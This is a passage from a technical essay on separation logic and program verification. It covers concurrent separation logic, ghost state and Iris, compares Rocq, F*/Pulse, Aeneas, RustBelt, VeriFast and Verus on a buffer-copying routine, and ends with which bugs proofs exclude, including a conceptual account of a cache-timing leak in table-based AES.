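C₁ ∥ C₂ means that C₁ and C₂ run in parallel. To prove something about two threads, we give each its own part of memory, prove each as if it ran alone, and combine the results. Like the frame rule, this method has a side condition, which is that neither thread changes a variable that appears in the other's code or assertions.

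In Brookes and O'Hearn's example, a parallel merge sort, two threads each sort one half of an array, and the program then merges the halves. The proof assigns each thread its own half, so it doesn't need to account for the order in which the threads take their steps. The rule for parallel threads would be unsound with an ordinary "and" in place of *, because each thread could then change memory that the other relied on. GPU kernels divide arrays among thousands of threads in the same way.

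### Locks that own memory

Most threads have to communicate at some point. The usual way to do this safely is with a lock, which only one thread can hold at a time. In concurrent separation logic each lock has a resource invariant I, which describes the memory that the lock protects. While no thread holds the lock, that memory belongs to the lock. A thread that takes the lock gains ownership of it, and must make I true again before letting go:

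```
If     {P * I}  C  {Q * I}
then   {P}  lock; C; unlock  {Q}
```

(The original rule is for a slightly more general construct, in which the thread also waits for a condition to become true.)

A lock can also hand memory from one thread to another. In an example from Brookes and O'Hearn, one thread allocates a pair of cells and puts its address into a buffer, and another thread takes the address out, uses the cells and frees them. The buffer's invariant is that either it is full and owns the pair at the address it contains, or it is empty and owns nothing. The proof then gives the two operations these specifications:

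{x ↦ –, –} put(x) {emp} and {emp} get(y) {y ↦ –, –}

After `put(x)` the sender still has the address in x, but it no longer owns the cells. If the sender used x again, perhaps after the other thread had freed the memory, the proof would fail at that line. The transfer of ownership appears only in the proof, not in the program's text.

This transfer made it hard to show that the logic was sound. O'Hearn tried for months without success, then asked Brookes, a specialist in the semantics of concurrency, to help. Brookes's proof requires every invariant to be precise, meaning that in any heap it picks out at most one part whose ownership could be transferred. Reynolds had found that without this requirement, the logic could prove something false if it also had Hoare logic's usual rule for combining two postconditions with "and". *Precision and the Conjunction Rule in Concurrent Separation Logic*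 (2011) later gave a single soundness proof for two versions of the logic, one that keeps this rule and requires precise invariants, and one that drops the rule and allows any invariant.

Many threads can safely read the same cell if none of them writes to it, but x ↦ v gives the cell to just one thread. Fractional permissions let threads share it by splitting x ↦ v into two halves, x ↦½ v * x ↦½ v, which can be split again. A thread with any fraction can read the cell, but it needs the whole to write. So while one thread holds the whole, no other thread can read the cell. Two fractions of the same cell must agree on its contents, and they can be rejoined when the readers have finished. Kapoor, Lodaya and Reddy, in *Fine-grained concurrency with Separation Logic*, describe the underlying idea as shared ownership on condition that the operations don't interfere.

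### Two threads and one counter

Suppose that a cell at address c contains 0, and two threads each run

```
lock;  t := [c];  [c] := t + 1;  unlock
```

where each thread has its own variable t. When both have finished, the counter should be 2. The lock matters, because without it both threads could read 0 and both write 1.

The lock has to own the counter, so its invariant must include c ↦ n for some n. If the invariant also limits n to some set of values, that set has to contain 0, because the counter starts there. Each thread has to restore the invariant after adding 1, whatever value it found, so if the set contains n it must also contain n + 1, and therefore every natural number. The invariant can guarantee that the final value isn't negative, but it can't exclude 7.

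The missing fact is that each thread adds 1 only once. No memory cell records this history, so the proof adds its own record, called ghost state, which the program never reads and which doesn't exist at run time. Owicki and Gries used auxiliary variables for such purposes in the 1970s.

For the counter, let a be a ghost variable for the amount that thread 1 has added so far, and b one for thread 2. Both begin at 0. The invariant owns half of each, and is now that for some m and n,

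c ↦ m + n * a ↦½ m * b ↦½ n

Thread 1 owns the other half of a, and thread 2 the other half of b. The proof for thread 1 is

```
{a ↦½ 0}
lock;
{a ↦½ 0  *  c ↦ m + n  *  a ↦½ m  *  b ↦½ n}
{a ↦ 0   *  c ↦ n      *  b ↦½ n}               since the halves agree, m = 0
t := [c];  [c] := t + 1;
{a ↦ 0   *  c ↦ n + 1  *  b ↦½ n}
{a ↦ 1   *  c ↦ 1 + n  *  b ↦½ n}               ghost update: a becomes 1
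unlock
{a ↦½ 1}
```

After the write, the counter is n + 1 but the ghost variables still add up to n, so the invariant no longer holds. Thread 1 has both halves of a at that moment, so it can change a to 1, which restores the invariant. It then gives half of a back to the lock and keeps the other half as evidence that it incremented the counter.

The proof for thread 2 is the same with b in place of a. Once both threads have finished, the main program owns a ↦½ 1 and b ↦½ 1. If it takes the lock, the halves must agree, so m = 1, n = 1, and the counter contains 2. Thread 2 could not have changed a, because it never owned the half that thread 1 kept.

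### Iris and user-defined ghost state

Half-owned ghost variables are enough for this counter, but other programs need other kinds of records, such as a token that only one thread can hold or a history that can only grow. For some years researchers designed new logics to handle these, each with its own rules and difficult soundness proof. Matthew Parkinson complained in 2010 that every new library or concurrency primitive seemed to need a new separation logic.

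Iris, begun in 2014, is an attempt to replace the many separation logics for concurrent programs with one. *Iris from the ground up* (Jung, Krebbers and colleagues, 2018) explains that the logic has two main ingredients: ghost state, which exists only in the proof and whose structure the user chooses, and invariants, which connect ghost state to real memory. Iris is a library for the Rocq proof assistant, which checks the proofs.

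The user chooses the structure of ghost state by defining a resource algebra. This is a set of elements with an operation · that combines what different threads own, and a rule for which elements are valid. The order of combination must not matter, and any part of a valid combination must itself be valid. (Each element may also have a "core", the part of it that threads can copy freely.) Three general rules then apply:

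1. Owning a · b is the same as owning a * owning b, so threads can divide ghost state between them.
2. Nobody can own an invalid element, so if two assertions would combine into one, the situation they describe is impossible.
3. An owner may change a to b only if b is compatible with everything that a was compatible with. Jung and colleagues call this a frame-preserving update.

The ghost variables for the counter fit this scheme. An element is a pair (q, m) of a fraction and a number. Two pairs combine by adding their fractions, and the result is valid only if the numbers agree and the total is at most 1. A thread that owns (½, 0) can't change it to (½, 1), because another thread may own (½, 0), which is incompatible with (½, 1). A thread that owns (1, 0) can change it to (1, 1), because no pair is compatible with (1, 0).

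Jung and colleagues use a different example, a cell x that starts unset and that threads can set only once. Once a thread has read a value from x, it should be able to rely on x keeping that value. Their algebra has elements called *pending* and *shot(n)*. Nothing can combine with *pending*, so at most one party owns it. *Shot(n)* combined with itself is still *shot(n)*, so any number of threads can have copies, but *shot(n)* and *shot(m)* are incompatible when n ≠ m. The owner of *pending* can change it to *shot(n)*, and nobody can change it back. The invariant is that either x is unset and the invariant owns *pending*, or x contains some n and the invariant owns *shot(n)*.

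When a thread sets x to n, the proof uses up *pending* and leaves *shot(n)* in the invariant. A thread that reads n takes a copy of *shot(n)*. If it reads x again later, x cannot be unset, because the invariant would then own *pending*, which is incompatible with the thread's copy. If x contains m, the invariant owns *shot(m)*, which is compatible with the copy only if m = n, so the thread must read n again. The same three rules govern both *pending*, which is a permission, and *shot(n)*, which is a piece of knowledge.

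Any thread may use an Iris invariant without holding a lock, but only for a single atomic step, which no other thread can interrupt, and it must restore the invariant by the end of that step. This suits programs whose threads coordinate through instructions such as compare-and-set, which writes a new value into a cell only if the cell still contains an expected old value. A lock is then an ordinary program built from such instructions, and its rule is a theorem provable in Iris.

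Unlike Reynolds's logic, Iris lets a proof discard assertions about memory, because P * Q implies P. Ordinary Iris triples therefore don't show that a program frees everything it allocates. In Reynolds's logic, a proof that a program starts with emp and ends with emp shows that it leaked nothing.

Work built on Iris includes verified C programs, crash-safe storage, hypervisors and parts of Rust's standard library, according to *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification* (Kan, Kan and Ertel, 2026), a paper mainly about getting AI systems to write such proofs. The Iris Project's 2026 publications include extensions of Iris to programs that make random choices and a logical foundation for Verus, a verifier for Rust.

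### What step-indexing is for

Some programs store functions in memory, and those functions may use other shared memory. An invariant that describes a memory cell holding such a function may have to contain a Hoare triple or another invariant. Iris allows this, but the meaning of assertions then becomes circular, because an assertion is a condition on resources, including ghost state, and the ghost state can contain assertions.

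Jung and colleagues prove that letting ghost state hold any assertion directly leads to a contradiction. One could then create a ghost location containing the assertion "the assertion stored in this location is false". This is the liar's paradox, and one could prove anything from it.

Step-indexing removes this circularity. Instead of being simply true or false, an assertion is true or false for each number n of remaining program steps. True for n means that running the program for n more steps can't show the assertion to be false. When ghost state contains an assertion, the meaning of that ghost state for n steps may depend only on the stored assertion's meaning for fewer than n steps. The definition therefore always refers to a smaller number, like a recursive function that terminates because its argument shrinks. The paradox no longer works, because opening the ghost location reveals the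 stored assertion only one step later.

The numbers make the definition of truth well-founded and are unrelated to how fast a program runs. In proofs they appear as the symbol ▷, read "later". Jung and colleagues say users can generally ignore this symbol unless they put triples or invariants inside invariants.

### Termination, deadlock and weak memory

The triples for concurrent programs express partial correctness, so a program that never finishes satisfies any postcondition, provided it causes no memory fault. For sequential programs, Reynolds defines a total version of the triple, which also requires the program to finish. The list reversal satisfies it because the list at i gets shorter on every pass. In 2008, Brotherston, Bornat and Calcagno developed a method for proving termination in separation logic. Termination is harder to prove in Iris because step-indexing describes what happens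 within any given number of steps, whereas termination means that some number of steps is enough. The extension Transfinite Iris addresses this by letting the step counts go beyond the finite numbers.

Concurrent programs can fail to finish because of deadlock. If one thread holds lock A and waits for lock B, while another holds B and waits for A, both wait forever. Both threads can still have valid proofs in the basic logic, because the rule for locks covers what a thread owns once it has the lock, but doesn't guarantee that it will ever get it. One remedy is to put all the locks in a fixed order and prove that every thread takes them in that order. LinearActris, a logic built on Iris, rules out deadlock for programs whose threads communicate by sending messages.

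Brookes's soundness proof and the basic version of Iris both assume that threads take turns, and that each step acts on one memory that every thread sees in the same state. Real processors reorder reads and writes to save time, a behavior called weak memory. Suppose two memory cells, data and flag, both start at 0. One thread writes 1 to data and then 1 to flag. Another thread waits until it sees 1 in flag and then reads data. Under the proofs' assumption, the second thread must read 1, but on an Arm processor it can read 0 unless the programmer adds instructions that enforce the order.

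Programs that do all their sharing through locks are mostly safe from this. Languages such as C++ and Java guarantee that if such a program has no data races, it behaves as if its threads took turns. A data race occurs when two threads access the same cell without synchronisation and at least one of them writes to it. A proof in concurrent separation logic shows that there are no data races. The risk is in code that works without locks, including the code that implements locks. There, an Iris invariant meant to hold "at all times" has no clear meaning if threads can see different contents in memory. In 2017, Kaiser and colleagues used Iris to build a logic for weak memory, in which an assertion can depend on which writes a thread has seen. Later researchers extended the safety proof for Rust to weak memory.

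## Four ways to combine the two

Verifying a real program with dependent types and separation logic requires connecting them to each other and to the programming language. Researchers have done this in several ways. A routine that copies n bytes from one buffer to another can illustrate how these approaches differ.

In C the routine is called `memcpy`. According to IBM's *memcpy()*, a manual page, its behaviour is undefined if the two buffers overlap, which means that the C language lets the program do anything at all in that case. Write a ↦* s for "the array at address a contains the sequence s". In separation logic, the specification is

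{dst ↦* d * src ↦*q s} copy(dst, src, n) {dst ↦* s * src ↦*q s}

where d and s both have length n. The q is a fractional permission, so the routine may read the source but not write to it. The precondition also excludes overlap. A cell in both buffers would need the whole permission for `dst` and a further fraction for `src`, which adds up to more than one.

### A program logic inside a proof assistant

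Rocq has no built-in notion of memory or of a running program, so someone has to define a programming language inside it. Iris comes with a small one called HeapLang. Its programs are values of an inductive type, like the vectors in the Lean examples, and its semantics is a relation that lists every step a program can take. For instance, `x <- v` can take a step if the heap has a cell at x, and that step stores v in the cell. If there is no such cell, the program is stuck, meaning it can't take a step, which is how the semantics represents a memory fault.

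With the syntax slightly simplified, the copying routine in Iris's array library is

```
copy dst src n :=
  if n ≤ 0 then ()
  else  dst <- !src;
        copy (dst + 1) (src + 1) (n − 1)
```

where `!src` reads the cell at `src`.

Iris defines triples through weakest preconditions, an idea that Dijkstra introduced in 1975. The assertion wp e {Φ} is the weakest condition under which the program e runs without a fault and any result it returns satisfies Φ. (Working backwards through the swap program was a way of calculating one.) Leaving out some bookkeeping, the definition has two cases:

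1. If e has already finished with the value v, then wp e {Φ} means Φ(v).
2. Otherwise, e must be able to take a step in any heap that agrees with what the threads own. After any step it might take, what they own must still agree with the heap, and wp must hold of the rest of the program, one step later.

The triple {P} e {Q} then means that owning P is enough to establish wp e {Q}. The frame rule and the other rules become theorems about this definition, and Rocq checks their proofs.

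The proof for `copy` is by induction on n. If n is 0, both sequences are empty and there is nothing to do. Otherwise, the proof splits the first cell off each array. The read needs some fraction of the source cell and the write needs the whole destination cell, and the precondition provides both. The frame rule sets these two cells aside while the induction hypothesis covers the remaining n − 1 cells of each array. Because n shrinks with every call, the library can state the theorem with a total version of wp, which also guarantees that the routine terminates.

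This theorem is still a statement in Iris's logic, and its meaning depends on ghost state and step-indexing. A sceptic may reasonably ask what it implies about actual runs. The answer comes from the adequacy theorem, which turns a proof inside the program logic into a plain statement about how the program runs:

> Suppose Iris proves wp e {φ} without assumptions, where φ is an ordinary condition on the result. Then no thread gets stuck in any run of e, and if the main thread finishes with the value v, φ(v) is true.

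Suppose that e creates an array containing 0, 0, 0 and another containing 7, 8, 9, copies the second into the first, and returns the first array's middle element. If φ(v) is "v = 8", the adequacy theorem gives a result stated only in terms of HeapLang's step relation and the number 8, without the separating conjunction or ghost state. Nobody has to trust Iris's rules, because an unsound rule would have made the adequacy theorem impossible to prove. The trusted base consists of Rocq's proof kernel, the definition of HeapLang, and φ.

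The weak point is the definition of HeapLang, a research language. Its integers have no maximum, its cells hold whole values instead of bytes, and its threads take turns. Verifying C in the same way requires a faithful definition of C, which is much larger. The Verified Software Toolchain (VST), another Rocq project, uses CompCert's definition of C, so a VST proof can combine with CompCert's theorem to cover the assembly code that the compiler produces. Ebner, Martínez and colleagues (2025) note in *PulseCore* that VST's developers recently rebuilt it on top of Iris, partly to gain more advanced ghost state and invariants.

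### Separation logic in a program's type

Iris users normally prove things about programs in a language defined inside Rocq, so each program and its proof are separate objects. The alternative is to add memory and threads to a dependently typed language and put preconditions and postconditions into the types of its programs.

The obstacle is that programs which use memory may also loop forever, and an endless loop can "prove" that 1 = 0. Hoare Type Theory, which Nanevski, Morrisett and Birkedal introduced in 2006, avoids this by giving computations a type of their own:

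{P} x : A {Q}

A value of this type describes a computation that may run when memory satisfies P. If it finishes, it returns some x of type A and leaves memory satisfying Q. A looping computation can have the type {emp} x : (1 = 0) {emp}, but it isn't a proof that 1 = 0. Getting the proof x would require running the computation, which never returns. Two years later, a system called Ynot added such types to Rocq.

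F* took up the idea. Swamy, Rastogi and colleagues (2021), in *SteelCore*, built a concurrent separation logic within F* that applies to F* programs themselves, and a language called Steel used it. Its successor is Pulse. A chapter of the Pulse tutorial, F*'s *Mutable Arrays*, includes the copying routine, whose type is roughly

```
fn copy2 (a1 a2 : array t) (l : SZ.t) (#p2 : perm)
  requires a1 ↦ s1 ** a2 ↦{p2} s2 **
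           pure (length s1 = length s2 = l)
  ensures  a1 ↦ s2 ** a2 ↦{p2} s2
```

Here `**` is the separating conjunction, and `pure` marks a fact that isn't about memory. The body is an ordinary `while` loop. The programmer supplies the loop invariant, mainly that the first i elements of `a1` equal those of `a2`. Pulse applies the frame rule automatically and leaves the arithmetic to Z3. If the programmer wrote to `a2` by mistake, F* would reject the program because p2 might be less than the whole permission. At the end, the invariant establishes that the two sequences agree at every position, but the programmer still has to call a lemma to conclude that they are equal.

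An older version of the routine shows what separation logic contributes. It appears in F*'s *Example*, a page about Low*, which is a subset of F* for C-like code. Low* has no separation logic, so the routine's precondition needs separate clauses to require that both buffers are allocated, that they are disjoint, and that they have the right lengths. The postcondition states again that both are allocated and adds that the routine modified only the destination. The loop invariant repeats most of this. In Pulse, the two ↦ assertions and the `**` between them cover everything except the lengths.

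Putting specifications in types helps more when a program takes other programs as arguments. Ebner and colleagues give the example of a task pool, which runs tasks in parallel. Its `spawn` function accepts a task with any precondition and postcondition. The caller gives up the memory described by the precondition and receives a handle. Calling `await` on that handle later returns whatever the postcondition describes. To copy a large buffer, a program could split the source and destination arrays in half, spawn a task to copy each half, and recover all the memory by awaiting both tasks. The specification of `spawn` covers this use and any other without mentioning arrays or copying.

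Ebner and colleagues formalised the underlying logic, PulseCore, in about 15,000 lines of F*. They used it to verify a further 31,000 lines of code, including hash tables, a parallel sorting program and a secure boot protocol. The trusted base contains F*, Z3, the tool that translates Pulse into C or Rust, and the C or Rust compiler. F* also checked the proof that PulseCore is sound, so a bug in Z3 could affect both that proof and the programs that rely on it.

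PulseCore proves only partial correctness for ordinary code. If the programmer forgot the line that increases i, the invariant would stay true on every pass, and the logic would accept a copying routine that never ends. Ghost code, however, must terminate, because the compiler erases it, and erasing an infinite loop would change what the program does.

Checking can also be slow. In *APAS-VERUS*, a talk about verifying a textbook's algorithms in Rust, Milnes says that proofs in F* and Pulse take about 12 times as long to check as his own in Verus. The comparison is informal, since the Pulse proofs were for a different textbook.

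### Letting Rust's compiler deal with memory

Much of the copying proof was about ownership, which the Rust compiler already checks in ordinary programs. Every Rust value has one owner, but other code can borrow it. A shared borrow, `&T`, normally allows only reading, and many can exist at once. A mutable borrow, `&mut T`, also allows writing, and no other code can use the value while it lasts. These borrowing rules resemble the rule for fractional permissions.

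In Rust the routine might be

```
fn copy(dst: &mut [u8], src: &[u8]) {
    let mut i = 0;
    while i < src.len() { dst[i] = src[i]; i += 1; }
}
```

The compiler rejects the call `copy(&mut a, &a)`, so nobody has to prove that the buffers don't overlap.

Aeneas, a tool for verifying Rust, makes use of this by translating safe Rust into pure functions in Lean. Ho, Fournet and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Verification of Cryptographic Software with Aeneas, Rust, and Lean*, describe how it works. A program called Charon extracts the Rust compiler's intermediate form of the code, and Aeneas turns each borrow into a plain value. The translated routine has a type like

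```
copy : Slice U8 → Slice U8 → Result (Slice U8)
```

It takes the contents of both buffers and returns the new contents of `dst`, wrapped in a `Result` because a Rust program panics (stops with an error) if it goes past the end of an array. The theorem to prove is that if the two slices have the same length, `copy dst src` succeeds and returns the contents of `src`. Neither the theorem nor its proof refers to memory.

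Functions that return a mutable borrow are harder to translate. Suppose `slot(dst, i)` returns a mutable borrow of the element at position i, and the caller then writes to it. The write changes `dst` after `slot` has returned. Aeneas therefore makes the translated `slot` return both the current element and a backward function that turns the element's final value into the final contents of `dst`. If `dst` is [0, 0, 0] and i is 1, the backward function maps any v to [0, v, 0]. When the caller writes 8 and the borrow ends, the translated program applies the backward function to 8 and gets [0, 8, 0].

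In the real program, `dst` changes at the moment of the write, but in the translation it changes only when the borrow ends. No program can observe the difference, because Rust doesn't let code use `dst` in the meantime.

Another model represents a mutable borrow by its current value and the value it will have when the borrow ends. *RustHornBelt* (Matsushita, Denis and colleagues, 2022) proved this model sound. The final value isn't known yet, so a "prophecy variable" f stands for it. When the program borrows position 1, the slice becomes [0, f, 0], and when the borrow ends, the proof gains the fact that f = 8. *VerusBelt* (Hance, Elbeheiry and colleagues, 2026) points out that if ghost code could read f, it could set the current value to f + 1. Ending the borrow would then make f equal to f + 1, and one could prove anything. *VerusBelt* therefore prevents ghost values from depending on prophecies.

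With Aeneas, Lean's kernel checks the proofs, but Ho and colleagues list other components that must also be trusted: the Rust compiler, Charon, Aeneas itself, two Lean tactics that run compiled code, and hand-written models of some library functions. Aeneas doesn't support raw pointers (addresses that the compiler doesn't track), concurrency, or types that allow mutation through a shared borrow. Someone has to write a model by hand for any function that uses these.

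Ho and colleagues ran into this limit in SymCrypt, Microsoft's cryptographic library, with a routine that wipes secret data by setting a buffer to zeros. The routine uses raw pointers and external code so that the compiler can't optimise the wiping away, so they assumed as an axiom that it sets every element to 0. The pure model also can't express why the wiping matters. A Lean function can return a slice of zeros, but the model has no memory in which an old copy of the secret might remain.

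### How RustBelt justifies unsafe code

Rust programmers normally copy bytes with the library function `copy_from_slice`. It calls a raw memory copy in a block marked `unsafe`, where the programmer may use raw pointers and is responsible for using them correctly. Many basic Rust libraries contain such blocks. This code doesn't follow the typing rules, so the usual argument for a type system, that a program which follows the rules can't cause a memory fault, doesn't apply to it.

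RustBelt, a 2018 project by Jung, Jourdan, Krebbers and Dreyer, replaced the typing rules with what the types mean. It gives each Rust type a meaning in Iris, namely an assertion about what someone owns when they have a value of that type. For `&mut [u8]`, this is ownership of the array's cells until the borrow ends. As Foroushaani and Jacobs (2022) explain in *Modular Formal Verification of Rust Programs with Unsafe Blocks*, the safety proof then has three steps:

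1. Show that every typing rule is true under these meanings.
2. Show, using the adequacy theorem, that a program which is well typed in this sense never causes a fault.
3. For each library that contains unsafe code, show that its functions live up to the meanings of their types.

For a function like `copy_from_slice`, step 3 means assuming ownership of the cells that the two argument types describe, and proving that the raw copy accesses no other cells and returns what it borrowed. Most of this follows from the triple for `copy`. The change that added the routine to Iris, *Add array_copy to heap_lang*, credits the `memcpy` proof in RustBelt's code as its model.

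RustBelt also gives each type a separate meaning for when it is shared. Rust's `Mutex`, for example, protects data with a lock and lets threads change that data through a shared borrow, which would be impossible if all shared borrows were read-only. Because `Mutex` has its own shared meaning, sharing one can amount to sharing a lock that owns the data, as in concurrent separation logic.

The proof covers a version of Rust with simpler data layouts and pointer rules. It supports the assumption Aeneas depends on, that Rust's rules prevent hidden aliasing, but it does not verify the code of Charon or Aeneas.

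### Automated verifiers

VeriFast, Viper and Verus, like F*, give up the small proof kernel to get more automation. The programmer adds specifications to the source code, the verifier works out what must be true for the code to meet them, and an SMT solver tries to prove it.

VeriFast works through a function line by line, using symbols in place of inputs. It keeps one list of the memory the function owns and another of the facts it knows. For a C version of the routine, when it reaches the line `dst[i] = src[i]`, it

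1. looks in the first list for permission to read the cell at `src[i]`, and for the whole cell at `dst[i]`;
2. uses Z3 to check that the known facts put i within both arrays;
3. records the new contents of `dst[i]`.

If either cell is missing, it reports an error on that line.

The programmer still has a fair amount to write. In *An Empirical Study of LLM-Generated Specifications for VeriFast* (Fan, Tran and colleagues, 2026), a C function that adds an element to the end of a linked list has 16 lines of code and 34 lines of annotations. Some annotations mark where VeriFast should unfold the recursive definition of a list or fold it up again. Others state and prove that two adjoining pieces of a list form one list, which VeriFast can't prove automatically.

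VeriFast supports C, Java and unsafe Rust, including multithreaded programs. Its scope includes a raw-pointer version of `copy`, which Aeneas can't translate. *Verifying purely unsafe Rust programs with VeriFast* (Jacobs, 2025) has chapters on byte arrays and loops over them. Foroushaani and Jacobs also extended VeriFast to check unsafe functions against the meanings RustBelt gives their types. This automates much of RustBelt's third step, but it requires trusting VeriFast as well as RustBelt's theory.

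Viper is an intermediate language. Other tools translate Python, Go or Rust into it, so they can share one verifier. Viper keeps permission to use memory separate from facts about what the memory contains. For `copy`, one clause grants permission to `dst[i]` for every i below n, and another states what those cells contain. Prusti, the Viper tool for Rust, is mainly for safe code.

Verus also uses Rust's ownership rules to avoid reasoning about memory. The specification of `copy` is close to the one for Aeneas, but it sits in the Rust source beside the code:

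```
fn copy(dst: &mut Vec<u8>, src: &Vec<u8>)
    requires old(dst).len() == src.len(),
    ensures  dst@ == src@,
```

`dst@` is the mathematical sequence that `dst` represents. The programmer adds a loop invariant, and Z3 does the rest.

Unlike Aeneas, Verus can verify code outside safe Rust, using an approach that Lattuada, Hance and colleagues (2023) introduced in *Verus*. The assertion x ↦ v becomes a Rust value of type `PointsTo`, which records an address and its contents. To write through a pointer, a program must supply a mutable borrow of the matching `PointsTo` value, while a shared borrow is enough for reading. The program can copy the pointer freely, but Rust's compiler stops it from copying the `PointsTo`. Verus erases these values before producing the final program, so they add no run-time overhead. Verus can therefore check ownership of raw memory with Rust's existing type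 checker and use Z3 to check ordinary facts about values.

Hance and colleagues proved in Iris that this approach is sound for a large part of Verus. Their main theorem is that a function which passes the checks and has a trivial precondition never causes undefined behaviour. The theorem covers an idealised Verus, not the implementation, so one still has to trust the code that translates Rust into logical conditions, the solvers, and the specifications that Verus assumes for library types such as `Vec`. The proof also leaves out the erasure of ghost code, where a bug might change what the program does, for instance by deleting an infinite loop. Milnes puts the trusted base at about 2 million lines, but this includes the Rust compiler and libraries, much of which Aeneas has to trust too.

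Verifying unsafe Rust can require less trust than this. Gäher, Sammler and colleagues (2024) verified a version of `Vec` with *RefinedRust*, which automates part of the work using tactics whose proofs Rocq checks. Hance and colleagues consider its automation weaker than that of SMT-based verifiers.

| | Iris and VST | Pulse | Aeneas | VeriFast, Viper and Verus |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Automation | Mostly tactics that a person or AI system chooses | Automatic framing, with Z3 for ordinary facts | No memory reasoning for safe Rust; Lean tactics for the rest | Z3 does most of the proof; people add invariants and hints |
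| Trusted base, besides the specification | Rocq's proof kernel and the language definition; for VST with CompCert, also the assembler and hardware | F*, Z3, translation to C or Rust, compiler | Lean's kernel and two compiled tactics, Charon, Aeneas, library models, Rust compiler | The verifier, its solver, library specifications, compiler |
| Languages | Any language that someone has defined in Rocq; C for VST | Pulse, which becomes C or Rust | Safe Rust | C, Java and Rust for VeriFast; several for Viper; Rust for Verus |
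| Unsafe or concurrent code | Both | Raw memory and concurrency | Neither, except through hand-written models | Both for VeriFast and Verus; varies among Viper's tools |

### Are dependent types necessary?

One can define a language, its program logic and an adequacy theorem without dependent types. Isabelle/HOL, which lacks them, has had separation logic for many years, and Klein, Kolanski and Boyton published a general library for it in 2012. A heap can be a function from addresses to contents, and an assertion a function from heaps to true or false. Defining these, P * Q or a step relation like HeapLang's doesn't require a type that mentions a value.

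The copying routine hardly uses them either. None of its versions gives the buffer a type indexed by its length, like `Vect`. In Iris and Pulse, the lengths are separate conditions, as they would be in Isabelle/HOL. Pulse uses a refinement type for array positions, but a precondition could express the same thing.

Dependent types help more with a function like `spawn`. In F*, a task's type contains its precondition and postcondition, so the type checker compares them with what the caller owns at every call. In Isabelle/HOL, one can prove a theorem about `spawn` for every precondition and postcondition, but someone must then apply it at each call. The two approaches can prove much the same things, but the type checker organises more of the work in F*.

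Dependent types also help with the mathematics. The cryptographic algorithm ML-KEM uses arithmetic modulo 3329, and other algorithms use other moduli. Lean's library has a type `ZMod p` for the integers modulo any number p, and Ho and colleagues use it in their proofs. In Isabelle/HOL, a type can't take an ordinary variable p as a parameter, so a theorem about every p needs a workaround, such as treating the integers modulo p as a set within a larger type. Unruh built With-Type to ease this kind of difficulty.

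The main argument for simpler types is that they are easier to work with. `append` would not have had its trouble with 0 + k if it had used ordinary lists instead of vectors. Simpler logics also suit automatic solvers. Verus specifications are close to first-order logic, which can express "for all numbers" but not "for all properties". Hance and colleagues note that programs that obey Rust's ownership rules can often have such specifications.

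The choice between Rocq and Isabelle/HOL therefore makes little difference to what anyone can prove about code that moves bytes between buffers. Good automation and a good model of the programming language probably matter more. The case for dependent types is stronger for libraries that accept arbitrary tasks and for code whose correctness depends on a lot of algebra.

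## Which bugs a proof excludes, and how proved programs still fail

A proof in any tool excludes only the bugs that its theorem covers. Every separation-logic proof rules out several kinds of memory fault. To exclude most other bugs, someone has to state and prove a further property.

| Bug | Theorem that excludes it | Does every separation-logic proof include it? |
|---|---|---|
| Out-of-bounds access | The program reads and writes only cells it owns | Yes |
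| Use after free | Freeing a cell uses up its ownership, so no later step can access it | Yes |
| Double free | Freeing a cell requires owning it | Yes |
| Data race | No thread writes to a cell while another can access it without synchronisation | Yes, if the logic covers threads |
| Integer overflow | Every result fits the machine's integer type | Only if the language model treats overflow as a fault |
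| Wrong result | If the program finishes, its result is the one the specification demands | No: needs a postcondition that fully describes the result |
| Memory leak | The program frees or hands over everything it allocates | No: needs a logic that can't discard memory |
| Deadlock or endless loop | Every thread eventually gets the locks it waits for, and finishes | No: needs total correctness, and an argument about locks |
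| Inconsistent data after a crash | After every step, the recovery program could repair what is on disk | No: needs a condition that holds throughout the run |
| Information leak | Two runs that differ only in their secrets look the same to an outsider | No: needs a comparison of two runs |
| Timing side channel | Two such runs take the same branches and access the same addresses | No: needs a comparison of two runs, preferably in machine code |

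HeapLang's integers have no maximum, so a proof about a HeapLang program can't detect an overflow. A verifier for C can treat signed integer overflow as a fault, as the C standard does.

A proof that covers crashes needs a separate crash condition, because a power cut can stop a program between any two steps, before its postcondition is true. The proof has to show that the data on disk meets the crash condition after every step, and that the recovery program works from any state that meets it.

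### Why leaks need a stricter logic

Suppose a function allocates a cell, stores 1 in it, and returns without freeing the cell or passing on its address. Reynolds's rule for allocation gives

{emp} x := cons(1) {x ↦ 1}

To show that the function leaves no memory allocated, we must prove the postcondition emp. But x ↦ 1 doesn't imply emp, so the proof can't continue until the programmer adds `dispose x`.

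Iris lets a proof discard assertions about memory. Since x ↦ 1 is the same as emp * x ↦ 1, the proof can drop x ↦ 1 and keep emp. The function then has the specification {emp} … {emp} even though its cell is still allocated. An assertion in Iris means that the program owns at least the memory described, so emp holds no matter what memory the program owns.

Dropping an assertion doesn't weaken the first four guarantees in the table, since a program that gives up a cell can touch less memory than before. It also suits garbage-collected languages, where programs don't free memory themselves. But when assertions can be dropped, a program can satisfy those guarantees without ever freeing memory. For instance, it can't use a cell after freeing it, because it never frees one.

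Even in Reynolds's logic, a proof rules out leaks only if the postcondition accounts for all the memory that remains. The assertion `true` holds of every heap, so `{emp} x := cons(1) {true}` is a valid triple even though the command never frees the cell it allocates. A server could also add every request to a list that it never reads again. It still owns the list, so this isn't a leak in the logic's sense, but the server will eventually run out of memory.

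### How a correct cipher can leak its key

AES, a very widely used cipher, has many software versions that rely on lookup tables. At one point such a program combines a byte p of the message with a byte k of the key and reads entry p ⊕ k of a table. (The operation ⊕, exclusive or, flips each bit of p where k has a 1.)

Suppose the table has 256 entries of four bytes each. Processors keep recently used memory in a fast cache, typically in lines of 64 bytes, so the table fills 16 lines with 16 entries each. An attacker running a program on the same processor can push the table out of the cache, let the cipher run, and then use timing to learn which line the cipher brought back. The line's number is the upper four bits of p ⊕ k. If those bits are 1010 and the attacker knows that p begins with 0011, then k begins with 1001. A real cipher makes many lookups, so the attacker needs many messages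 to tell them apart, but each message narrows down the key.

The cipher always returned the right ciphertext, so a proof of its functional correctness is still valid. A Hoare triple relates the state before a run to the state after it, and the usual models leave out both the cache and execution time.

*On the Promises of 'High-Assurance' Cryptography* (Symbolic Software, 2026) mentions another example, KyberSlash. This flaw in the reference code for Kyber, the algorithm behind the ML-KEM standard, came to light in late 2023. The code divided secret-dependent numbers by 3329, and on some processors the time a division takes depends on the number being divided.

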